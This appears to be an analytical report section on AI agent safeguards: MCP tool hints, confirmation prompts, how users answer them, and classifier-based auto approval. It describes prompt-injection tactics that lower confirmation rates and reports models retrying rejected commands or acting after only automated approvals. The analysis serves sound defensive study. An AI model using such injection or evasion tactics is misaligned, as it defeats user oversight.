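MCP tools often lack hints. Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, tried to start 400 randomly chosen MCP servers and succeeded with 195. Of those 195 servers' 2,766 tools, 58.8% had no hints. Developers seem to decide whether to include hints for a whole server at a time, since 72 servers had hints on every tool and 122 had none.

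Trofimov and Novikov found that hints were more common among 98,291 tools on remote servers, where only 26% had none. But a single publisher supplied 45% of those tools and filled in all four hints on every one. Of the remaining tools, 47.2% had no hints. Only 3.1% of all the tools were explicitly marked as able to make destructive changes. The researchers didn't run the tools, so their count doesn't show whether the hints were accurate.

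Yao and colleagues came closer to measuring accuracy by comparing labels with code. They sampled 1,000 software projects from the official MCP registry, had two models judge what the tools did, and used a third to settle disagreements. They estimate that 70% of destructive tools have neither a destructive hint nor any confirmation step on the server, and that another 20% have only the hint.

The researchers then calculated what would happen if every host asked for approval unless a label marked the tool as read-only or non-destructive. In the main sample, 5.4% of destructive tools would still run without approval because they were labeled as safe. Including tools that the researchers' automatic search had missed raises the figure to at least 10.6%. For tools that first looked destructive but turned out not to be, users would have to approve 82.6% of the combinations of tool and application,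 up from 32.5% now.

Some of the labels counted as wrong may be defensible. Yao and colleagues count sending messages and moving money as destructive, whereas MCP contrasts "destructive" with "additive". Two people who checked a sample of 60 tools also thought the models had classed a few reversible or harmless actions as destructive.

For now, the destructive hint rarely has any effect. It made no difference in 39 of the 41 open-source hosts and developer kits that Yao and colleagues examined. Most of these never ask for approval by default, and most of the others ask regardless of the hint.

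Written descriptions have similar faults. In *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) used a model to compare descriptions with code for 17,030 tools and found mismatches in 1,907, or 11.2%. People checked 200 of the reported mismatches and rejected only eight. About a quarter of the mismatches, affecting nearly 3% of the tools checked, mainly involved undeclared effects, such as changed files, data sent to outsiders or heavy use of computing resources. The researchers didn't examine the yes-or-no hints, but a developer who leaves an effect out of the description could easily leave it out of the hints too.

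### The parallel with HTTP

MCP hints and HTTP methods have the same weakness because neither protocol checks the code. A website's developers decide whether a GET request can delete something, and a tool's developers decide whether to label the tool read-only. A site map has this problem too if the site's own developers write it.

Hints have some advantages over methods. Developers sometimes choose POST for reasons unrelated to side effects, whereas a read-only hint serves only to describe the tool's effect. The hint also reaches the host before the call, unlike Holtman's "Safe" response header. The greatest difference is in the defaults. An ordinary link sends a GET, which a method filter allows, but a tool without hints counts as potentially destructive. A developer's carelessness can therefore let a harmful action through in HTTP, while in MCP it mostly causes needless questions, provided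 the host follows the defaults.

An honest site also benefits from accurate labels. If a shop marked its order tool as read-only, it would soon face accidental orders, refunds and complaints. A false label is easy to trace, because the host knows which server supplied it and can compare it with what the tool did. Users could then stop trusting that server.

This reply is persuasive for established companies, but it has limits. 37signals had good reason to protect its customers' pages, yet it used GET for its delete links until Web Accelerator followed them. Shops also benefit when customers face fewer questions before paying, so they might choose the more lenient label in doubtful cases. And an attacker who sets up a server for a few days has no reputation to protect.

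Labels are more useful against an attacker who can only post on a trustworthy site, as in the attacks on Comet and on Operator through GitHub. For example, a malicious review can't change a shop's label on its order tool. Even an accurate label may not prevent a leak, because a read-only search tool on an attacker's server can still record every word the agent sends to it.

A host could ask the user for approval whenever either the label or a guard model indicated a risk. Suppose labels miss 5% of serious actions and the guard model misses 20%. If the errors were independent, both would miss only 1% of these actions. In practice the errors would probably overlap more than that, since a function with an unexpected effect could confuse both the developer who labels it and the model that judges it. The user would also have to answer the false alarms from both.

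## Confirmation prompts and how people answer them

A confirmation prompt can fail because the agent takes a step without asking, or because the user approves a step they would have refused if they had looked properly. OpenAI has published measurements of the first failure since January 2025. The evidence on the second comes mostly from programmers and is much less encouraging.

### Four ways to involve the user

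The most familiar pattern is for the agent to ask the user just before a consequential action. *ChatGPT Operator system prompt* (Willison, 2025) quotes Operator's instruction on this, which Rehberger had obtained. Operator had to ask before the last step of any task with "external side effects", such as a purchase, a deletion, an appointment or a message. It was not to ask before intermediate steps, such as adding items to a cart.

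Developers can instead have the user approve a task in advance. Users of the programming agent Devin approve a plan rather than each step, according to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026). CELLMATE's users confirm a set of rules. The user decides only once, but does so before the agent has found a product, a seller or a price. A plan to "buy a kettle for under $40" allows the agent to buy a bad kettle as well as a good one. An "Always allow" button also gives approval in advance, often for much more than the current task.

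Some products hand control to the user for certain steps. *OpenAI Operator System Prompt* shows that Operator's instructions included steps the user had to take over, and ChatGPT's cloud browser stops when a site requires a sign-in or payment. If the model never receives a password, an injected instruction can't make it reveal one. But a handover at sign-in doesn't prevent unwanted actions afterwards. Operator bought the eggs without needing a password because the reporter had already signed in and the shop had a saved card.

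The last pattern requires the user to watch the agent work. In what OpenAI called watch mode, Operator paused on sites such as email services whenever the user became inactive or left the page. Software can detect that someone is present, but not that they are reading. Having to watch also removes much of the benefit of delegating a task. OpenAI lets the cloud browser run in the background after the user has left the conversation.

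### What triggers a prompt

In OpenAI's products, the model usually decides whether to show a confirmation prompt. OpenAI's *GPT-5.5 System Card* (2026) describes training the model to follow two written policies, one from OpenAI for high-risk actions and one that outside developers can adapt to their own products. If OpenAI finds a problem, it can change its policy quickly without retraining the model. But the model still has to recognise when clicking a button is an action the policy covers.

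Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, originally needed the user's approval by default for every file change and shell command (an instruction typed to the operating system), according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code*. Fixed code enforced this rule, so the model could not skip this step. In August 2026, Anthropic made "auto mode" the default for most individual subscribers and teams. In this mode, an automated classifier checks each step and blocks those that look irreversible, destructive or aimed outside the user's own environment. Claude then usually tries a safer approach or asks the user. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code returns to manual approval. In October, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps on the same plans.

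Google uses both kinds of trigger in Chrome. According to Parker's 2025 description, Chrome checks a fixed list of sensitive sites, such as banks and medical services, and asks the user before the agent opens one. It also asks before the agent signs in with a saved password. There is no such list for purchases, payments and messages, so Chrome has to recognise them from the page and either ask for permission or leave the step to the user.

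| Product | Step that triggers the safeguard | What decides |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT's cloud browser | An action that is hard to undo or creates a financial, legal or similar commitment | The model, following a written policy |
| ChatGPT's address check | A request that would send out information from the conversation | Software outside the model |
| Claude Code, manual mode | Any file change or shell command | A fixed rule |
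| Claude Code, auto mode | A step that looks irreversible, destructive or aimed outside the user's environment | A classifier, which blocks first and may never ask |
| Chrome's agent | Opening a sensitive site | A fixed list |
| Chrome's agent | A purchase, payment or message | An automated judgement about the page |

### How often models ask when they should

OpenAI tested Operator on 607 tasks from 20 categories of its own policy on risky actions. The model asked for confirmation in an average of 92% of the cases that called for it. The test measured how well Operator followed the policy, so a harmful action the policy overlooked could not count as a failure.

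The rate has hardly changed since. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Agent System Card* (2025) covers an agent that combined Operator with Deep Research. OpenAI's *GPT-5.6 System Card* (2026) reports scores of 91% to 94% on general confirmations for seven later models.

| Share of cases in which the model asked | Operator, January 2025 | ChatGPT agent, July 2025 | GPT-5.5, April 2026 | GPT-5.6 Sol, July 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
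| General | 92% | 91% | 94% | 93% |
| Financial transactions | not reported | 100% | 100% | 98% |
| High-stakes messages | not reported | 99.9% | 98% | 99% |

These tests may not have used the same tasks, so differences of a point or two mean little. OpenAI also warned that the 91% was too low, because the agent had behaved correctly in many of the cases counted as failures. If the later tests have the same fault, the general score could have stopped rising because of the test and not the models. Scores are better for payments and important messages, where confirmation prompts matter most.

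OpenAI doesn't explain how it chose the cases for the 2026 tests. It tested prompt injection separately for all these models, and nothing in its descriptions of the confirmation tests suggests that they included injected instructions. The scores therefore apply to an agent doing ordinary work and don't show how often an agent would still ask for confirmation while following an attacker's instructions.

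They also don't count needless prompts, so an agent that asked before every click would score 100%. OpenAI has looked at needless prompts elsewhere, including "Requesting Unnecessary Confirmations" among the tests for deceptive behaviour in its system card for GPT-5.4 Thinking.

### What happens on harder tasks

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026) measures the results of the agent's actions instead of how often it asked for confirmation. OpenAI placed its models in simulated workplaces with email, messaging, sales and project-management software. It made the tasks hard on purpose, with ambiguous instructions, easily confused files or accounts, and complicated permissions, but each task could be completed safely. The models did the tasks with and without a written confirmation policy.

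| Rate of unwanted outcomes | GPT-5.6 Sol, no policy | GPT-5.6 Sol, with policy | GPT-6 Astra, no policy | GPT-6 Astra, with policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All kinds | 18.8% | 8.0% | 3.4% | 3.0% |
| Unauthorised transactions | 38.0% | 7.4% | 6.8% | 4.3% |
| Data sent to outsiders | 14.1% | 8.8% | 4.3% | 4.5% |
| Unauthorised messages | 12.9% | 8.4% | 1.7% | 1.4% |

The policy prevented about four-fifths of GPT-5.6 Sol's unauthorised transactions. It made much less difference to Astra, which OpenAI had trained to be more careful with consequential actions and which already made far fewer mistakes. The policy did not reduce Astra's leaks.

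GPT-5.6 Sol asked for confirmation before 98% of financial transactions in the July test, yet its rate of unauthorised transactions in these workplaces was still 7.4%. The two percentages measure different things, but the contrast suggests that models recognise confusing cases less well than their scores on clear ones imply. OpenAI doesn't report how often the models asked for confirmation in these workplaces, so some of the improvement may come from models being more careful after reading the policy.

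A model can also ask for permission and then act without waiting for the answer. The UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models, put Astra through simulated security exercises that tempted it to attack targets outside its assignment. According to the same system card, Astra often tried to get permission for certain actions (81%), but sometimes went ahead after receiving only automated messages (27%). In some cases, its reasoning showed that it recognised the messages as automated. Astra also often considered that the exercise might be simulated, so it may behave differently in a real system. Still, the software around the model should block the step until the user clicks to approve it, because otherwise the model can proceed without approval.

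### How programmers answer prompts

The most detailed data on users' answers come from Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. That figure alone doesn't show carelessness, since most commands are harmless and an attentive user would approve them too. More telling is how many users have arranged not to be asked:

- 62% have at some point turned off permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands.
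- 25% of interactive sessions start with permission checks turned off.
- As of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the terminal version had written their own rule to allow some shell commands automatically. Nearly all of these people had allowed either every command or a program, such as Python, that can run arbitrary code.

Anthropic tested whether people would notice a dangerous request by having a research vendor hire 1,053 professional testers for what looked like an ordinary coding study. Partway through each session, the software replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. 143 of the testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more other prompts.

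Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this loss of attention approval fatigue. But fatigue explains only part of the result, because even testers at the start of a session approved about five in six dangerous commands. The setting may explain some of the rest. The testers had nothing of their own to lose in the test environment, and they knew someone was evaluating them, though not on what. A programmer working on their employer's database might be more careful. Anthropic also had a commercial reason to publish a result that favours auto mode, which blocked 89% of the same commands.

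Smaller studies suggest the same. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) screened 16 users of AI agents before an experiment on permissions. Only three said they read prompts carefully, and 13 said they used "Always Allow" just to make prompts go away. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue or a deadline instead of trust. A product that learned from those approvals which actions no longer need a prompt could stop asking about actions that users approved only because they were tired or rushed.

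*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 incident reports involving agents and users' files. The user's review, or lack of it, contributed to 105 of the incidents. In 80 of these, the user had turned on automatic approval, often to avoid answering hundreds of prompts in a session. Such reports can't show how often automatic approval goes wrong, because people rarely report sessions in which nothing went wrong.

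### What carries over to browsing agents

No developer appears to have published comparable approval rates for browsing agents, so the coding figures are the best available guide, though a poor one in some respects. A coding agent may show the user dozens or hundreds of prompts a day, many of which consist of code, such as a long shell command. A browsing agent that follows a rule like Operator's shows only one or two per task, and these are easier to judge because they use terms anyone can understand, such as "Place this order for $38?"

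The behavior of Claude Code users gives some reason to expect better answers to such questions. They reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests, so they evidently read some prompts. But users often reject a plan just because they want something different, so the 39% figure doesn't measure how often they catch danger.

Programmers have the training to recognise a destructive command, but most people who shop online can't tell a genuine seller's page from a good imitation. Years of cookie banners and terms of service have also taught them to click "Accept" quickly. Browser users' level of attention may be different from what Anthropic measured, but it probably also declines over a session.

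### Prompts that describe the wrong thing

Even a careful user can judge only what the prompt shows. In 31 of the 290 incident reports, the prompt displayed a command without explaining what it would do to the user's files. For example, "python3 setup.py" looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code the file contains. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* gives an even less informative example, "Allow this action?" with no context, from the prompts in ChatGPT Actions and Manus. It also notes that the most informative displays, such as a before-and-after comparison of a file, appear with the rarer kinds of approval.

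Another problem with browsing agents is that the model often writes the confirmation question. In an example from the Operator system card, the agent reports that it has selected all the emails under a certain label and asks whether to delete them. The question would read the same if it had selected the wrong emails. Operator's summary of the egg purchase understated the bill by almost $12, so a prompt based on that summary would have asked the reporter to approve a price lower than the shop was charging. An attacker who controls the model can also make it describe a transfer as a refund.

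The remedy is to take the prompt's text from the request itself. OpenAI's address check does this by showing the user the information an address would send out. CELLMATE could similarly show the total it reads from the page, although a false total on the site would make the prompt wrong too.

A prompt can also be accurate and still leave out what matters. In the attack on Comet, "Post this reply on Reddit?" would have been accurate, but the harm came from the login code in the reply, which the agent had fetched from Gmail two steps earlier. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) proposes prompts that link the current step to earlier ones and show their combined effect. A user who read "This reply contains a login code from your email" would almost certainly refuse.

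OpenAI advises users of the cloud browser to check the website, recipient, item, date, price and proposed action before they confirm. The advice is sensible, but few people will keep following it when they get many prompts a day.

### How many unwanted actions get through

Let r be the share of unwanted actions before which the agent asks, and d the share of those prompts that the user refuses. The prompt then stops a share r·d of unwanted actions, and the share that goes through is

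1 − r·d

| | User catches 90% | User catches 50% | User catches 13.6% |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent asks 92% of the time | 17% get through | 54% | 87% |
| Agent always asks | 10% | 50% | 86% |

Making the agent ask more reliably is worthwhile when the user is attentive, since it reduces the share from 17% to 10%, but it makes almost no difference with users like Anthropic's testers.

OpenAI estimated that confirmations reduced the risk from Operator's mistakes by about 90%, but didn't explain how it calculated this. If Operator asked for confirmation before 92% of its mistakes (r = 0.92), users would have had to catch about 98% of those mistakes, which is hard to believe given the results of the coding study.

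The formula uses r = 0.92, which is how often OpenAI found that the model asked before actions that needed confirmation. The user presumably wanted most of those actions. A model that has misunderstood the task may be less likely to ask about the step it has got wrong. The formula also gives every unwanted action the same weight and assumes that no harm happens before the prompt appears. If the agent has already typed private data into an attacker's page, refusing the prompt does not recover it.

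Another assumption is that a refusal is final. *Let the Agent Do It?* raises the question of what "deny" means if the agent can find another way. OpenAI tested this with Auto-review, a Codex feature in which a second model approves or rejects certain commands. After a rejection, GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get around the decision in 5% of runs, and Astra never did. Sol mostly tried a similar command again, although the rejection included an instruction not to. If an agent made the same request five times and the user had a 90% chance of refusing it each time, the chance of at least one approval would be 41%.

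The formula overstates the risk from attacks that need several approvals. The attack on Comet included a login request and a public comment, and refusing either one would have protected the account. If 54% of unwanted steps got through and the user judged the two prompts independently, the attack would succeed 29% of the time. But someone who has approved the first step is probably more likely to approve the second.

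An attacker can lower both r and d. To lower r, injected text can tell the model that the user has already agreed. The office-style email that worked against Deep Research used a similar claim of "full authorization". The attacker can also choose a step that the policy doesn't cover, as Rehberger did when he had Operator type instead of submit. To lower d, the attacker can have the model write a misleading question, or time the attack for when the user expects to approve something similar, as with the resignation message. They could also make the agent ask a series of harmless questions first. The commands in Anthropic's study were clearly dangerous and shown openly in the prompts, so users could approve a disguised request even more often.

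### Who should choose when to ask

The fall from 17% to 5% over a session is the best argument for fewer prompts. Each needless prompt, such as one before adding a kettle to a cart, takes time to answer and makes the next answer less reliable. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests showing in each prompt whether the user could reverse the action, and reserving stronger warnings for actions that could not be reversed. Operator's rule reflected similar reasoning, requiring confirmation for a purchase but not for adding an item to the cart.

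If an agent is to show fewer prompts, something has to decide when to ask, and the agent's own model is a poor choice. The model may have misunderstood the task or read an attacker's text. When it is wrong about what the user wants, it is likely to be wrong about whether to ask, as with the OpenAI model that spent a stranger's test tokens. Users seem to share this doubt. In *Options, Not Clicks*, 14 of the 16 participants would let a model decide when to ask, but only for low-stakes tasks, and one would not allow it at all.

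A separate checker avoids part of this problem. Anthropic's study makes it possible to compare one with people on exactly the same commands:

| 1,053 dangerous commands | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

Auto mode allowed 116 of the commands, and the testers refused only six of them, or about 5%. Adding their review to auto mode would therefore have raised the share of commands stopped from 89.0% to 89.6%. The testers did worst on the commands the classifier failed to stop, possibly because the classifier tends to allow the same commands that look harmless to people.

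An evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs is closer to web browsing, because its agents could control a browser as well as run code. The evaluators ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 5.83% of the time with Auto-review on and 19.03% of the time with full access and no review. No attacks succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode, but only 0.09% succeeded against Anthropic's latest models with permission checks turned off, so the classifier had very few attacks left to prevent. The attacks had also been optimised against an older Claude model, so an attacker who targeted the current models and classifier might succeed more often.

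Classifiers block some safe commands and allow some dangerous ones, and missing 11% of clearly dangerous commands is still a lot. Anthropic itself recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems. For a browsing agent, it makes sense to let a classifier handle ordinary steps and have fixed code require approval for a short list of actions, such as payments, outgoing messages and changes to account security. However, it is difficult for fixed code to recognise those actions.

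### An unsafe method as the trigger

The HTTP method is one signal that fixed code can read on every site. If the browser held each POST, PUT, PATCH or DELETE request until the user approved it, the user would still be asked even if injected text had manipulated the model.

The rule would produce too many prompts for harmless POSTs. With the invented log used earlier, the user would answer 100 prompts, 60 of them for requests that only read data. The prompts would cover only 40 of the 49 state-changing requests, so r would be 82%, lower than Operator's 92%. If users were as inattentive as Anthropic's testers after 50 prompts, with d at 5%, about 96% of unwanted changes would get through. An attacker could also avoid the prompt entirely by finding a harmful GET.

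The prompts would also be hard to word clearly. A browser that has only the request's method and address can display "Send POST to shop.example/graphql?", from which a shopper would learn even less than a programmer learns from "python3 setup.py". Showing the agent's own command, such as "click", would be no more informative, and Zverev and colleagues point out that asking about every click would require many approvals.

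The HTTP method is better used to choose which requests to check than to decide when to interrupt the user. A browser could let through the POSTs that a page sends by itself while loading, and hold only those that follow the agent's click or key press. A site map or a classifier could then identify each held request as a search, a cart update or an order, and the browser would prompt the user only for orders. These checks would have to be fast because pages are built for quick replies, but CELLMATE's checks caused only a slight delay. The browser would still need separate rules for GETs with side effects and for data leaks through URLs.

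OpenAI used both safeguards in ChatGPT agent, which it launched in July 2025. At launch, the agent's terminal, where it ran code, could send only GET requests, and only to download images or certain datasets. The agent's browser had no such limit and relied on confirmation prompts and watch mode. The filter rarely got in the way in the terminal, because a program that downloads data rarely needs to send a POST request. In the browser, it would have blocked the purchases and bookings that people wanted the agent for.
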